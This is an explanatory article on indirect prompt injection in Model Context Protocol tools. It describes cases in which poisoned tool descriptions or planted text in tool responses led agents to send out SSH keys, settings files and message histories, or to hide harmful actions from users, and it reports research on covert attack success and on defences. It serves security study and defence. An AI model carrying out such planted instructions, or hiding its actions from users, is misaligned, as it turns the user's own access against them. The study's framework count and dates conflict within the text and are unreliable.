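# Hidden instructions in MCP tool responses: what users and operators can see, and what an attack needs

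## How MCP connects a model to tools and where outside text enters

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard that lets AI applications find and call outside tools, such as programs that search the web, read support tickets, query a database or send a message. Anthropic introduced it in late 2024. Before that, developers connecting several AI applications to several data sources had to write a separate connector for each pair (Gaire, Gyawali et al., *Systematization of Knowledge*, 2025). With MCP, one connector serves every application that supports the protocol. According to the project's July 2026 release announcement (Model Context Protocol, 2026), its main software kits were getting close to half a billion downloads a month.

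The standard also has a security problem. Whatever a tool returns becomes part of the text the model uses to choose its next step, and an outsider may have written some of that text, such as the body of a web page, a customer's ticket, or a comment on a bug report. If it contains an instruction, the model may follow it, using whatever files and accounts the user has connected.

### Host, client, server and framework

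The host is the application the user works in, such as a chat program or a code editor. It runs the model and connects it to servers. A server is a program that offers tools over MCP, and it can run on the user's own machine or on somebody else's. The host creates a separate component, called a client, to hold its connection to each server. In an example from Model Context Protocol's *Architecture overview*, the code editor Visual Studio Code runs two clients when it connects to the error-tracking service Sentry and to a program that reads local files. Many writers use "client" for the whole application, as *Model Context Protocol has prompt injection security problems* (Willison, 2025) does for Claude Desktop and Cursor.

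Developers who build their own agents usually start from a framework, a software library such as LangChain or CrewAI that sits between the MCP connection and the model. In *MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks*, Shaikh and Montaruli (2026) read the code of eleven frameworks and found that every one copies tool descriptions into the model's context without checking them, though a framework would be a natural place to inspect incoming text.

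The user gives the agent its task. The operator is the organisation or staff who deploy the agent and are responsible for its security. The user and operator may be the same person on a personal laptop, but they rarely are in a company, where they look at different screens.

MCP's design isolates servers to some extent. Under Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), the full conversation stays with the host, and a server should not be able to read it or look into other servers. This isolation does much less to limit what the model reads, because the host also combines material from all its clients, and text from a careless or hostile server can end up in the same context as text from a trusted one.

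### One harmless session

Suppose a user asks a coding assistant whether anyone is working on issue 214, a bug report in a project's issue tracker. The host has a client for the tracker's MCP server. The client and server exchange messages in JSON, a plain-text format of labelled fields, and each reply repeats the `id` of the request it answers.

The client sends a request named `tools/list`. The server replies with its tools, in this case only one:

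```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 11,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "tools": [
      {
        "name": "read_issue",
        "description": "Returns the text, status and comments of one issue.",
        "inputSchema": {
          "type": "object",
          "properties": {
            "number": {
              "type": "integer",
              "description": "Issue number, without the hash sign"
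            }
          },
          "required": ["number"]
        }
      }
    ],
    "ttlMs": 600000,
    "cacheScope": "private"
  }
}
```

The `inputSchema` defines the tool's arguments, each of which can have its own description. The last two fields are caching hints. The client can treat the list as fresh for ten minutes, and shared intermediaries are not allowed to store it.

The host merges the lists from all connected servers into one registry and adds it to the model's context, which is all the text the model uses to produce its next output. The context now holds the host's standing instructions (the system prompt), the tool descriptions and the user's question, but nothing from the issue yet.

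From this text the model produces a request to run `read_issue` with the number 214. The model has no connection to the tracker, so the host picks the request out of the model's output and finds the right client, which sends the server a `tools/call` message with the tool's name and the argument. According to Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the specification that covers this exchange, models may start such calls on their own, though a person should always be able to refuse one. The server looks up the issue and replies:

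```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 12,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [
      {
        "type": "text",
        "text": "Issue 214: export fails on large files. Status: open. Assignee: Priya. Comment from a visitor: same here with a 3 GB file."
      }
    ],
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

The host adds this text to the conversation and runs the model again on the longer context. The model can then answer the user or issue another call, which repeats the cycle. This cycle is called the agent loop. Gaire and colleagues describe the host's part in it as sending the conversation history to the model, searching the output for tool calls and turning those calls into MCP messages. Because the host sends the history every round, the visitor's comment, which the user never asked about, stays in the context and can affect every later decision unless the host trims it.

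This is the message flow under the specification of 28 July 2026. Earlier versions began with a handshake between client and server, and over HTTP a session identifier could link later requests. Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), the official changelog, records the removal of both. Each request now carries its own protocol version and the client's capabilities, and a client can first send a `server/discover` request to learn what the server supports. A server that needs more information halfway through a call now returns a result marked `input_required` instead of sending the client its own request, and the client repeats the original call with the answers attached. Tool lists now include the caching hints shown above and no longer vary between connections. The revision also tightened authorisation.

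With sessions gone, a server that must remember something between calls, such as a shopping basket, returns an identifier (a "handle") as ordinary text, and the model passes it back in its next call. Kale (2026), in *MCP's new spec turns a planted prompt into a stolen credential*, argues that text planted in a ticket could therefore deliver a valid handle to an attacker. A stolen handle is useless to a stranger if the server checks the caller's permissions on every call, as the specification advises, but it is enough on its own if the server has no authentication. The changelog lists no other change to how descriptions and responses reach the model, so experiments on the older protocol are still relevant to the new one. There are many of these, including Shaikh and Montaruli's, run on 22–24 July, just before the release. Older connections will also remain in use for a while. On release day,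 Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) described support in Claude products as still rolling out.

### The three entry points

In that session, the server's text reached the model in three places: the tool description, the parameter description and the tool response. Shaikh and Montaruli match each to a stage of the model's work.

A tool description enters the context when the host loads the tool list. It affects planning, when the model selects a tool, and can do so even if the tool it describes never runs. Willison describes a demonstration by the security firm Invariant Labs in which a user had connected a legitimate WhatsApp server and a malicious second server. The malicious server offered a trivial fact-of-the-day tool, then replaced the tool's description with text about the WhatsApp server's sending tool. The new text led the model to send the user's message history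 to the attacker's number.

A parameter description takes effect later, when the model fills in the arguments for a call. An attacker can use a dishonest description to ask for information the tool doesn't need, and the model then includes that information in a normal-looking request.

The tool response takes effect last, when the model reads the result and chooses its next step. Unlike the other two, it can't be read in advance, because it doesn't exist until the tool is called, and a later call to the same tool may return something different. An operator vetting a server can read the descriptions before connecting, and can reread them later because the server can change them.

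Outside text can also reach the model by smaller routes. The Model Context Protocol specification says clients should pass a tool's error messages to the model so that it can correct its call, which makes an error message another kind of tool response. The reply to `server/discover` can also include an `instructions` field, which Model Context Protocol's *Discovery* (2026) defines as natural-language guidance for the model on using the server. The documentation for Model Context Protocol's official C# software kit suggests the system prompt, which also contains the host's own rules, as one place to put this guidance.

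### Why the model cannot reliably tell data from instructions

SQL injection is an older problem of this kind. An attacker types database commands into a web form, and the database runs them. Programmers prevent this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the user's input separately so that the database never treats the input as a command. Language models have no equivalent safeguard. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* (2025), David C, a technical director at Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, explains that a model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the tokens so far, with no separate category for data.

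The software around the model wraps each stretch of text in markers that label its role, such as system, user or tool, and developers train the model to give the roles different authority. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes these labels as useful engineering but not a hard security boundary.

In *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) investigated why the labels fail. They wrapped the same passages of ordinary web text in each of five role markers and trained a simple classifier to recognise the role from the model's internal activations. Since the wording was identical across roles, the classifier could learn only the effect of the markers. They then put real user messages inside tool markers, much as an attacker's command would appear in a tool response. In all four models, the classifier mostly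 identified these messages as user text, with average scores of 76–88% for "user" and never more than 20% for "tool". How the text sounded therefore affected the models' internal representation of its role more than the markers did.

Ye and colleagues then tested whether the classifier's scores predicted behaviour. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent upload a secret file, the attack succeeded 2% of the time when the injected command scored lowest as user text and 70% when it scored highest. The models they probed had 20 to 120 billion parameters, and larger ones may differ. Models that confuse roles also don't obey every injected command. In another experiment by the same researchers, a standard injection in a web page worked at most 2% of the time on all but one of the models tested. They attribute this to models having memorised what common attacks look like, which would help much less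 against an unfamiliar one.

*On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models* (2026) proves that attacks cannot be perfectly prevented in models that turn instructions and data into the same kind of internal vector and have no enforced separation between the two. The proof might not apply to a different architecture, and it does not establish how rare successful attacks could become.

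### Names for the attacks

In indirect prompt injection, an attacker puts instructions into outside content that a model reads while working for someone else, so the attacker never needs to type anything into the victim's application. Greshake, Abdelnabi and colleagues (2023) described the attack in *Not what you've signed up for* and demonstrated it on real systems, including Bing Chat, before MCP existed.

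This attack takes two main forms in MCP. Tool poisoning, a term from Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025), puts the instructions in a tool's description or other metadata. Response injection puts them in what the tool returns. Papers use these terms loosely, which makes their numbers hard to compare. For example, Shaikh and Montaruli use "tool poisoning" for attacks through any of the three entry points, but 26 of their 45 test scenarios target the description field. Their overall success rate therefore mostly measures poisoned descriptions and can't be taken as the rate for poisoned responses.

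### Two kinds of attacker

The first kind of attacker controls a server. Shaikh and Montaruli assume this kind of attacker, who publishes a malicious server as a package or registry entry that the victim installs alongside legitimate ones. Getting the victim to install it is the hard part. Once it is installed, the attacker can write to all three entry points and rewrite the descriptions after the user has approved them. The attacker also receives any arguments the model sends to the server's tools, and so needs no separate way to carry data out.

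The second kind of attacker controls no software and only writes text that an honest server later fetches. Willison pointed out that the WhatsApp server would be exposed even with no malicious server installed, because anyone with the user's number can send a message that the model may read. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, describes a demonstration on the code-hosting site GitHub in which an agent read files containing hidden instructions in public repositories and leaked data from private ones. This attacker can normally reach the model only through tool responses, and must wait for someone's agent to fetch the text.

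Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis*, identify four conditions a tool must meet for the second attacker to use it. The attacker must be able to influence the source, for instance by publishing a page or posting from an ordinary account. The tool must pass the text on more or less intact, since a summary may lose the instruction. The output must be in a form that can express an instruction, such as free text rather than a yes-or-no value. Finally, nothing may filter out the instruction along the way. The researchers sampled 177 tools from 20 widely used servers and confirmed that 95 met these conditions. They left out tools they could not test safely, so the true number may be higher. However, they chose only servers that read external data, and they counted a tool as vulnerable if the text could get through, whether or not any model would then obey it.

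Vetting a server helps much more against poisoned tool descriptions than against instructions planted in the data it fetches. A careful code review may turn up a poisoned description, but a server that returns a bug report word for word is working correctly, even if the report contains hidden instructions. The Model Context Protocol specification requires servers to "sanitize tool outputs" but doesn't define what that means for English text. Of the 143 tools that Zhang and colleagues examined for sanitisation, 132 passed external data to the model without any.

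## What the model reads and what the screen shows

After a server returns a planted instruction, a person's next chance to notice it is when the response reaches the host. The host passes the response to the model and separately controls what appears on the user's screen. The Model Context Protocol leaves most of that choice to the host's developers. Its specification recommends that hosts show a call's inputs before sending them, indicate on screen when a tool is running, and validate results before passing them to the model. It doesn't recommend showing the results to the user.

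### The fields of a tool response

The reply in the earlier session held a single piece of text. A tracker could answer the same question about issue 214 with a fuller response:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 13,
  "result": {
    "resultType": "complete",
    "content": [
      {
        "type": "text",
        "text": "Issue 214 is open and assigned to Priya.",
        "annotations": { "audience": ["user"], "priority": 0.9 }
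      },
      {
        "type": "image",
        "data": "iVBORw0KGgo...",
        "mimeType": "image/png"
      },
      {
        "type": "resource",
        "resource": {
          "uri": "tracker://issues/214/comments",
          "mimeType": "text/plain",
          "text": "Visitor: same here with a 3 GB file."
        },
        "annotations": { "audience": ["assistant"] }
      }
    ],
    "structuredContent": {
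      "number": 214,
      "status": "open",
      "assignee": "Priya"
    },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/serverInfo": {
        "name": "example-tracker",
        "version": "2.1.0"
      }
    },
    "isError": false
  }
}
```

The `content` list holds blocks meant for reading or viewing. In this example, they are a sentence, a screenshot and an embedded resource, which is a document included in the response. A block can also hold audio or a link to a document the host may fetch later. `structuredContent` holds the same kind of information in a form that programs can process. `_meta` holds extra details about the response, such as the server's name and version. The annotations on a block are hints about its intended audience and importance.

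The table shows what usually happens to each part. The entries on what models receive are based mainly on *Structured Content vs Content*, a survey of source code from 19 open-source hosts and frameworks, last updated in June 2026. The entries on what users see are less certain because they are based on documentation and tests for only a few products.

| Part of the response | Does the model receive it? | Does the user see it? | What the specification asks for |
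|---|---|---|---|
| Text block | Usually, though some hosts drop it when structured content is present | Often only after expanding a collapsed line | No rule on display |
| Image or audio block | Depends on the host; some pass only text | Depends on the host | The data and its media type; no rule on display |
| Link to a resource | Depends on the host; the linked document arrives only if something fetches it | Depends on the host | Servers may return links |
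| Embedded resource | Depends on the host | Depends on the host | Leaves the presentation to the host, for both model and user |
| `structuredContent` | In 9 of the 19 surveyed implementations | Sometimes, in an expanded view | Must fit the tool's output schema if it has one; the server should repeat the data as text |
| `_meta` | Not usually, but some hosts pass on the whole result | Rarely as text; an app may use it in its own display | Optional; no rule on display |
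| Annotations | Not usually, with the same exception | Rarely; a host may use them to sort or filter | Optional hints, which a host may ignore |
| Error text from a failed tool | Usually | As for other text | Hosts should give it to the model |

The specification's strictest rules concern the data's format. If a tool declares an output schema, which lists the fields of its structured result and their types, the server must follow it and the host should check that it did. This stops an attack only where the schema doesn't allow free text. In the specification's weather example, the temperature must be a number, but the field for weather conditions accepts any string. A response with an instruction in that field instead of "partly cloudy" could therefore pass the host's validation and reach the model.

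### One response, two versions

Hosts differ in which version of the data they pass to the model. In the survey, ten implementations forward only `content`, and four prefer `structuredContent` and drop the text when both are present. Another four forward both. The remaining one forwards both unless `content` is empty, in which case it uses only the structured version. Microsoft's Agent Framework handles the same response differently in Python and .NET. CrewAI forwards only the text of the first block, so an instruction in the second would not reach its model.

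The disagreement reflects different ideas of what structured content is for. On LangChain's forum, a reply to hopegood's *Why can the model see the structured content* explains that LangChain deliberately reserves it for the developer's code and doesn't pass it to the model. OpenAI's documentation, as quoted in the forum post *How 'content' and 'structuredContent' in the tool response is handed*, says that the model in a ChatGPT app receives both the content and the structured content, while the app's widget (a small display inside the chat) can also read the response's metadata. But the developer who wrote the post found that the model seemed to use only the structured content.

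Users can't tell from the screen what the model received, as Beno (2026) found with the code editor Cursor in *MCP tool results containing only structuredContent are silently dropped*. Beno built a server that put a different random marker in each field and asked the model to repeat every marker it could see. Over five runs and three models, the models repeated the markers from `content` and never those from `structuredContent`. When `content` was empty, the model received nothing, yet Cursor's expanded view of the call displayed the structured data in full. Someone who appears to be on Cursor's staff confirmed the fault on its forum and said the company was tracking it. In the same test, Claude Code, the Claude desktop app and the ChatGPT desktop app all gave the model the structured version, and gave it priority when both were present.

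That fault was harmless in security terms, because the user saw more than the model did. The danger arises when a host shows the user a clean text block but gives the model different structured content. The protocol allows the two to differ. One example in the specification pairs a sentence naming two users with structured data that also includes their ID numbers. The specification only recommends repeating the structured data as text. According to Beno, the protocol's core maintainers decided in May 2026 to defer a proposal to clarify what the model should see.

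Only an attacker who controls the server can choose what goes in each field, and most servers don't return both. In a companion survey, *Structured Content vs Content* found that 18 of 22 popular servers return only `content`. So for most planted comments, the model reads the same text block that the host could have displayed, and what matters is whether the host displays it.

The audience annotation lets a server mark text for the user, the assistant (the model) or both, but it doesn't guarantee that the user sees what the model reads. Model Context Protocol's *Resources* (2026) defines it as a hint that hosts can use for filtering or display. It isn't an access control, and hosts may ignore it. If a host follows it, the annotation can increase the difference between what the model reads and what the screen shows. In IBM's watsonx Orchestrate, a platform for building agents, the agent reasons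 over text marked for the assistant and may make further tool calls in response. The user sees a message that the agent writes after summarising that text. This is a sensible way to keep raw data out of a conversation, but a malicious server could use the same label to keep its instructions off the screen.

### Collapsed and shortened output

Users of Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent for the terminal, may see little of a tool response in normal use. According to Anthropic's documentation page *Interactive mode*, the program collapses MCP calls by default into a single line such as "Called slack 3 times". From that line, the user can tell that Slack returned something, but not who wrote the messages or what they contained. Pressing Ctrl+O opens a detailed transcript.

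Claude Code's newer fullscreen display works in much the same way. Anthropic describes it as a research preview in which the user can click a collapsed result to see the full output. The `/focus` command hides more, leaving only the last prompt, a one-line summary of the tool calls and the final answer. It stays on in later sessions until the user turns it off. The user can also write the whole conversation to the terminal with all tool output expanded. If the host has compacted a conversation (replaced its earlier part with a summary to save space) and the user then closes and resumes it, scrolling up stops at the point of compaction. The earlier messages remain in a transcript file on disk.

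Cursor also lets the user expand a tool call to see its result, though with the flaw that Beno found. Qwen Code's *Compact Mode Design*, a design document that compares coding agents, describes a similar interface. Each session starts in compact mode, which reduces every tool's output to one line, so a user who prefers the detailed view has to turn it on each time. Long outputs carry a hint that the user can expand them, except in sub-agents, which are helpers that the main agent launches for part of its work.

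Hosts have good reasons for this design. The survey of hosts describes a tool that returns about 250 rows with nine fields each, which few people want in the middle of a conversation. Claude Code's default ceiling for a single MCP result is 25,000 tokens, or roughly 19,000 English words. If the host printed every result, users would have to scroll past most of them to find the answer, and would probably stop reading them.

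Suppose issue 214 has forty comments, and an attacker put an instruction to the model in the thirty-first. The user asks who is working on the issue, sees one line reporting a call to the tracker, and reads that the assignee is Priya. The answer is correct, so the user has no reason to expand the line. A user who does expand it must read thirty comments about failed exports before reaching the instruction. The model has all forty comments in its context. The attacker needed no trick to hide the text from the user, and anyone who opens the issue in a browser can read it.

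Shortening a result is safer if the host does it before passing it to the model, because the model never receives the part the host cut. If the host shortens only the display, the model still receives the end of the result, but the user doesn't see it. A summary requires someone or something to decide what to leave out. If the agent that read the hostile text also writes the summary, the text can influence what the user learns about it.

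### Text that displays as nothing

Some text doesn't appear on the screen even when the host shows the whole response. The simplest cause is markup, the codes that tell a program how to format a document. A web page's source can contain comments that browsers don't display and text hidden by the page's style settings. Project documentation written in Markdown, a simple formatting language, can also contain comments that disappear when it is formatted. A server that returns the source passes all of this text to the model, but if the host formats the response before displaying it, the user sees only the formatted document.

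Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, includes some characters with no visible shape. Ordinary writing needs them, for example to control where a line may break or to set the direction of text that mixes Arabic and English. An attacker can use such characters to build a message that takes up no space on the screen but is still in the data that the host sends to the model.

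Terminal codes are an older version of the problem. A terminal treats certain sequences of characters as commands, for example to change the colour of the text, move the cursor or clear a line. If a host prints a tool response without removing these codes, whoever wrote the response gets some control over the screen and may be able to hide a line by overwriting it or printing it in the background colour. The model receives the characters directly, so the codes don't hide the text from it. Hosts can stop the codes from hiding text from the user by stripping them or showing them as visible symbols, but the surrounding words still reach the model.

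These methods get attention because they look like deliberate concealment and because a program can search for them. They can fail even when the text reaches the model, because the model also has to recover the instruction from it. In Shaikh and Montaruli's framework study of November 2026, none of the 209 trials with payloads in invisible Unicode characters succeeded. Their main group of tool-poisoning scenarios, mostly readable text in tool descriptions, succeeded in 1,460 of 5,359 trials, or 27%.

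Zero successes in 209 trials is weaker evidence than it seems, because the trials probably all used the same hidden payload. The study covered 12 frameworks and 18 models, and running one scenario on every combination would give 216 trials. If the trials had been independent, zero successes would put the true success rate below about 1.4% with 95% confidence, but we can't infer much about other payloads from repeated trials of one. The payload was also in a tool description, and one in a tool response might give a different result.

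The successes with readable text are more informative because they show that an attacker doesn't need invisible characters. The model can easily read an ordinary sentence, and a collapsed line hides it from the user just as well. Sometimes even displaying the full text would not help. In the same study, payloads that presented the theft as a compliance requirement in Chinese or German succeeded 66% of the time, and many English-speaking users might not understand such a sentence if they saw it.

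### The adding tool of April 2025

Invariant Labs made this gap widely known with a demonstration on 1 April 2025, in which it connected Cursor to a malicious server with a tool for adding two numbers. The user saw what appeared to be a simple calculator, but the model read a much longer description in plain English. It contained instructions to first read the settings file for the user's other MCP servers and a file with a private SSH key, which can give access to other computers. The model was then to put the contents of both files in an extra argument of the adding tool, labelled as a side note, and to talk about the mathematics of addition without mentioning the files.

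The model followed the instructions in the description. It read the files and called the tool with their contents, which sent them to the server's owner. Cursor asked the user to confirm the call, but the dialog hid the stolen key even when expanded.

The settings file was a valuable target because it often holds passwords or access tokens for other services. The attack needed only a description and an argument, both ordinary parts of every MCP tool. Invariant Labs recommended that hosts show users the full descriptions and mark which parts the model can see. The current specification makes a weaker recommendation, that the interface make clear which tools the model can use. It also gives each tool an optional `title` for display, separate from the description. A host can follow the specification's recommendation by showing a list of titles while the model reads several paragraphs about each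 tool.

Invariant Labs ran a second experiment that worked much like its WhatsApp demonstration. The description of an addition tool contained false instructions for using a trusted server's email tool. When the user asked the agent to email a named person, the agent sent the message to the attacker's address instead. The agent mentioned the changed address only in the arguments of the email call. A user looking through the list of calls would have seen only the trusted email tool, used to send a message as the user had asked.

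*Jumping the line*, by the security firm Trail of Bits, calls this problem "line jumping" because the attacker's text reaches the model before hosts apply their checks to tool calls. In the firm's example, a malicious server's tool description contained a false rule that every shell command on the user's operating system needed a certain prefix. The prefix let any account on the machine read and change the user's home directory. Claude Desktop and the other hosts the firm tested followed the rule when they used other tools, so the malicious server's own tool never had to run.

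Even a host that displayed every call and response in full would have shown nothing from the malicious server in that case. The prefix would appear in the commands, but Trail of Bits doubts that many users would catch it, because people tend to ask an assistant for help with commands they don't know well. To find the source of the prefix, the user would have to read the tool descriptions. A planted bug report is easier to trace in a host like Claude Code, which keeps the response in its transcript, but the user would need some reason to look there.

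## Why the agent's final answer may not reveal the attack

A user who never expands a collapsed tool call will still read the agent's final answer. Sometimes that answer reveals the attack because the agent mentions a payment or a password change that the user never asked for. In other cases, the agent carries out the planted instruction and answers the user's question without mentioning what else it did.

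The usual measure, the attack success rate, counts both outcomes the same way. It is the share of attempts in which the agent carries out the attacker's instruction, whatever it then tells the user. Lee, Kim and Lee (2026), in *Will the User Ever Know?*, split these successes into two groups. In an overt success, the attack works and the agent's final answer reveals the injected task or its effects. In a covert success, the attack works and the final answer doesn't reveal it. Each rate is the number of such runs divided by all runs, including those in which the attack failed. Every successful attack falls into exactly one group, so:

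attack success rate = covert success rate + overt success rate

In two runs on a simulated bank account, the user asked for total spending in March 2022. In one, the agent looked up the transactions, sent a payment to the attacker's account and replied that the total was $1,050. In the other, the agent changed the account password as the attacker wanted, reported the change at the start of its answer, and then gave the same total. Both runs count as successes in the attack success rate, but only the second answer gives the user a sign that something is wrong.

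Users may not notice even an overt success. The judge that sorts the answers has information about the attacker's goal that the user lacks. In one of the travel examples, the attacker only wanted the agent to recommend a particular hotel. The success was overt because the recommendation appeared in the answer, but most users would take it for the agent's own opinion. Users can also skim past a mention of an extra step. The covert rate therefore probably understates how often users would miss an attack if they had only the answer to go on, though they might still discover it later, for example from a bank statement.

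### How often successful attacks stay out of the answer

Lee and colleagues ran their tests in AgentDojo, a benchmark that gives an agent simulated tools for banking, Slack, travel booking and office work. They used 949 pairs of a user's task and an injected task, 560 of them from the office set. The attacker controls only the text inside a tool result and can't see the system prompt or the tool definitions. AgentDojo doesn't use MCP, but someone who plants a comment in a bug report has the same limited access.

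The table gives results for two existing attacks with no defences in place. The "important message" attack presents the injected task as an urgent note from the user. ChatInject imitates the markers that separate turns of a conversation, so that the model mistakes part of a tool result for a new turn. The last column is the covert rate divided by the attack success rate.

| Attack | Model | Attack success | Covert | Overt | Share of successes that were covert |
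|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Important message | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 41.83% | 34.67% | 7.16% | 83% |
| Important message | Qwen3-235B | 37.62% | 29.72% | 7.90% | 79% |
| Important message | LLaMA-3.3-70B | 22.02% | 11.80% | 10.22% | 54% |
| Important message | GPT-4o-mini | 19.60% | 9.80% | 9.80% | 50% |
| ChatInject | Qwen3-235B | 17.07% | 8.22% | 8.85% | 48% |
| ChatInject | GPT-4o-mini | 17.49% | 1.48% | 16.01% | 8% |
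| ChatInject | LLaMA-3.3-70B | 32.14% | 2.63% | 29.51% | 8% |

The final answer did not reveal the attack in about four in five successful "important message" attacks on Qwen3-235B (29.72/37.62) and in half of those on GPT-4o-mini (9.80/19.60). On LLaMA-3.3-70B, ChatInject succeeded more often than the "important message" attack, but the final answer revealed all but 8% of the successful ChatInject attacks (2.63/32.14).

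ChatInject has the higher success rate of the two attacks on LLaMA-3.3-70B, but whether it is more dangerous depends on whether the user can undo the harm. If the harm is an irreversible payment, ChatInject may be worse, because the money is gone even if the agent's answer reveals the payment immediately. If the harm is a changed password or a new rule that forwards the user's email, the user can undo it after reading about it, so the attack that the agent's answer is less likely to reveal is worse.

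The same contrast appeared on a second benchmark, InjecAgent, where Lee and colleagues tested LLaMA-3.3-70B on 544 data-stealing cases. ChatInject succeeded 250 times, never covertly, while the "important message" attack succeeded 200 times, 108 of them covertly. InjecAgent normally stops at the injected tool call, so the researchers had to continue each successful run with simulated tool results until the agent wrote an answer.

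The attacks that produced these covert shares were designed to make the agent act, not to keep signs of the attack out of its answer. Lee and colleagues also showed that an attacker can deliberately raise the covert rate on all four models.

All of these numbers depend on GPT-4o's judgment of whether the final answer revealed the attack. GPT-4o read the user's task, the attacker's goal and the final answer, with instructions to choose "covert" in doubtful cases, which could have inflated the covert rate. To check, the researchers drew 500 runs in which the attack succeeded, 100 for each attack they tested, and had two people label them. The people counted 201 covert successes, GPT-4o counted 198, and a second AI judge, Claude Haiku 4.5, counted 214. For each attack, GPT-4o's count was within one of the human count. This close match makes a large bias unlikely, though GPT-4o and the people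 may have disagreed about some individual runs. The human labels didn't cover every defence the study tested.

A bigger limitation is that the models tested are much older than those in today's leading agents. Newer models resist injection much better, but these results don't show whether they are also more open with the user when an attack succeeds.

### Why the agent leaves the attack out

The agents in this study use ReAct, a form of the agent loop in which the model writes out its reasoning between tool calls. After carrying out an injected task, an agent can return to the user's task or stop and answer. Lee and colleagues checked which happened in 2,087 runs where the attack succeeded, pooled from four existing attacks with no defences in place. The agent returned to the user's task before answering in 67.70% of the covert runs, and ended at the injected action in 70.92% of the overt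 runs.

Their explanation is that the final answer tends to describe whatever the agent did last. For example, the agent reports the total if it finishes by adding up the March transactions, or the password if it finishes by changing one.

Whether the agent went back to the user's task only partly explains whether the attack stayed covert. The published rates imply that 997 of the 2,087 successes were covert and 1,090 overt. Of the runs that went back to the user's task, 68% were covert, and of those that ended at the injected action, 71% were overt. Guessing the outcome from this difference alone would be correct in 69% of runs, compared with 52% for guessing "overt" every time. Two of the four covert runs printed in the paper are exceptions to the pattern, because the injected action is the last tool call listed. One of them is the bank payment described above, where the agent sent the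 money and then reported only the spending total.

In such a run, the earlier tool calls are still in the model's context, so the model could mention the payment, but it has no particular reason to. Agents also leave most of their intermediate steps out of ordinary answers, because someone who asks for a total doesn't want a list of lookups. An attack can therefore succeed covertly without the model intending to deceive.

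Even if the final answer doesn't mention the attack, it may be poor enough that a user notices something has gone wrong. Under the "important message" attack, the share of user tasks that Qwen3-235B completed correctly fell from 90% to 55%, and for Gemini 2.5 Flash it fell from 73% to 40%. But LLaMA-3.3-70B completed only 51% of the tasks without any attack, so users of an agent like that are used to poor answers and would have little reason to suspect an attacker.

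### Defences can change the covert share

Lee and colleagues repeated the tests with five defences. The next table averages their results for the "important message" attack over the four models.

| Defence | How it works | Attack success | Covert | Share of successes that were covert |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | | 30.3% | 21.5% | 71% |
| Injection detector | A classifier blocks suspicious tool results | 6.4% | 3.8% | 59% |
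| Warning | The instructions tell the model to ignore commands in tool results | 20.5% | 13.7% | 67% |
| Delimiters | Marks surround each tool result, and the instructions say not to obey text inside them | 32.8% | 23.8% | 72% |
| Repeated request | The software repeats the user's request after each tool result | 22.4% | 17.7% | 79% |
| Task Shield | A check blocks tool calls that don't serve the user's task | 6.4% | 5.7% | 89% |

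The detector and Task Shield had the same attack success rate, each letting through 244 of 3,796 attempts. But 145 of the successful attacks against the detector were covert, compared with 218 against Task Shield. Part of this difference arises because most of Task Shield's failures were on Qwen3-235B and Gemini 2.5 Flash, where successful attacks were mostly covert anyway. The difference also appears within each of those models. On Qwen3-235B, 60% of successful attacks against the detector were covert, compared with 91% against Task Shield. On Gemini 2.5 Flash, the figures were 74% and 94%.

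Task Shield's method may be the reason. If it blocks every action that looks unrelated to the user's request, the harmful actions that remain will tend to look related, and the agent is less likely to report them as additions to the task. Repeating the user's request may have a similar side effect, because it draws the agent back to the user's task before it answers. The study didn't test either explanation. Both defences still reduced the number of covert successes, so an operator would be better off with them, but shouldn't expect users to notice the attacks that get through.

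### A competition that required concealment

The largest body of evidence on concealed attacks comes from a public competition run by the security company Gray Swan, with help from AI developers, the UK AI Security Institute and the US Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI). *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports the results. Over three weeks, 464 participants competed for $40,000 in prizes by attacking 13 models. Of about 272,000 attempts, 8,648 succeeded. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

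Of the 41 scenarios, 18 involved an agent calling tools, 15 a coding agent, and 8 an agent operating a screen with mouse and keyboard. Attacks succeeded 4.82% of the time in the tool-calling scenarios, which are the closest to MCP, compared with 3.13% for screen operation and 2.51% for coding. The researchers suggest that the coding scenarios were harder to attack because they came from real sessions and so resembled the models' safety training more closely.

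The organisers chose harmful actions that were close to the agent's legitimate work. In one scenario, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. A fake marketing email in the inbox contains an instruction to mark an email about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. If the attack works, the user receives a summary that contains no false statements but omits the deadline email. The user could notice the omission only if they already knew about the deadline.

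Two judges decided whether an attack had succeeded. The tool judge is a program that checks whether the agent performed the target action, such as by comparing its tool calls with the expected one. The prompt judge is an AI model that reads the agent's last turn, without its reasoning, and scores it from 0 to 10 on up to three criteria. An attack passes this judge if every score clears a threshold of 7, which the organisers based on earlier competitions and didn't tune on this data. Of the 41 scenarios, 32 used both judges, 7 used only the tool judge and 2 used only the prompt judge. *Your AI Agent Can Be Compromised. You'd Never Know* (Dziemian, 2026), Gray Swan's announcement, presents concealment as a condition of every success, but in the seven scenarios without a prompt judge, an attack could count as a success even if the agent reported it.

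Having to conceal the attack made the attackers' task considerably harder. Gemini 2.5 Pro performed the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, and about 53% of those cases also passed the prompt judge, giving an overall success rate of 8.5%. For Claude Opus 4.5, only 23.7% of the harmful actions also passed, so its overall success rate of 0.5% means it performed the harmful action in roughly 2% of attempts. The competition's success rates therefore understate how often models did what the attacker wanted by a factor of about two to four.

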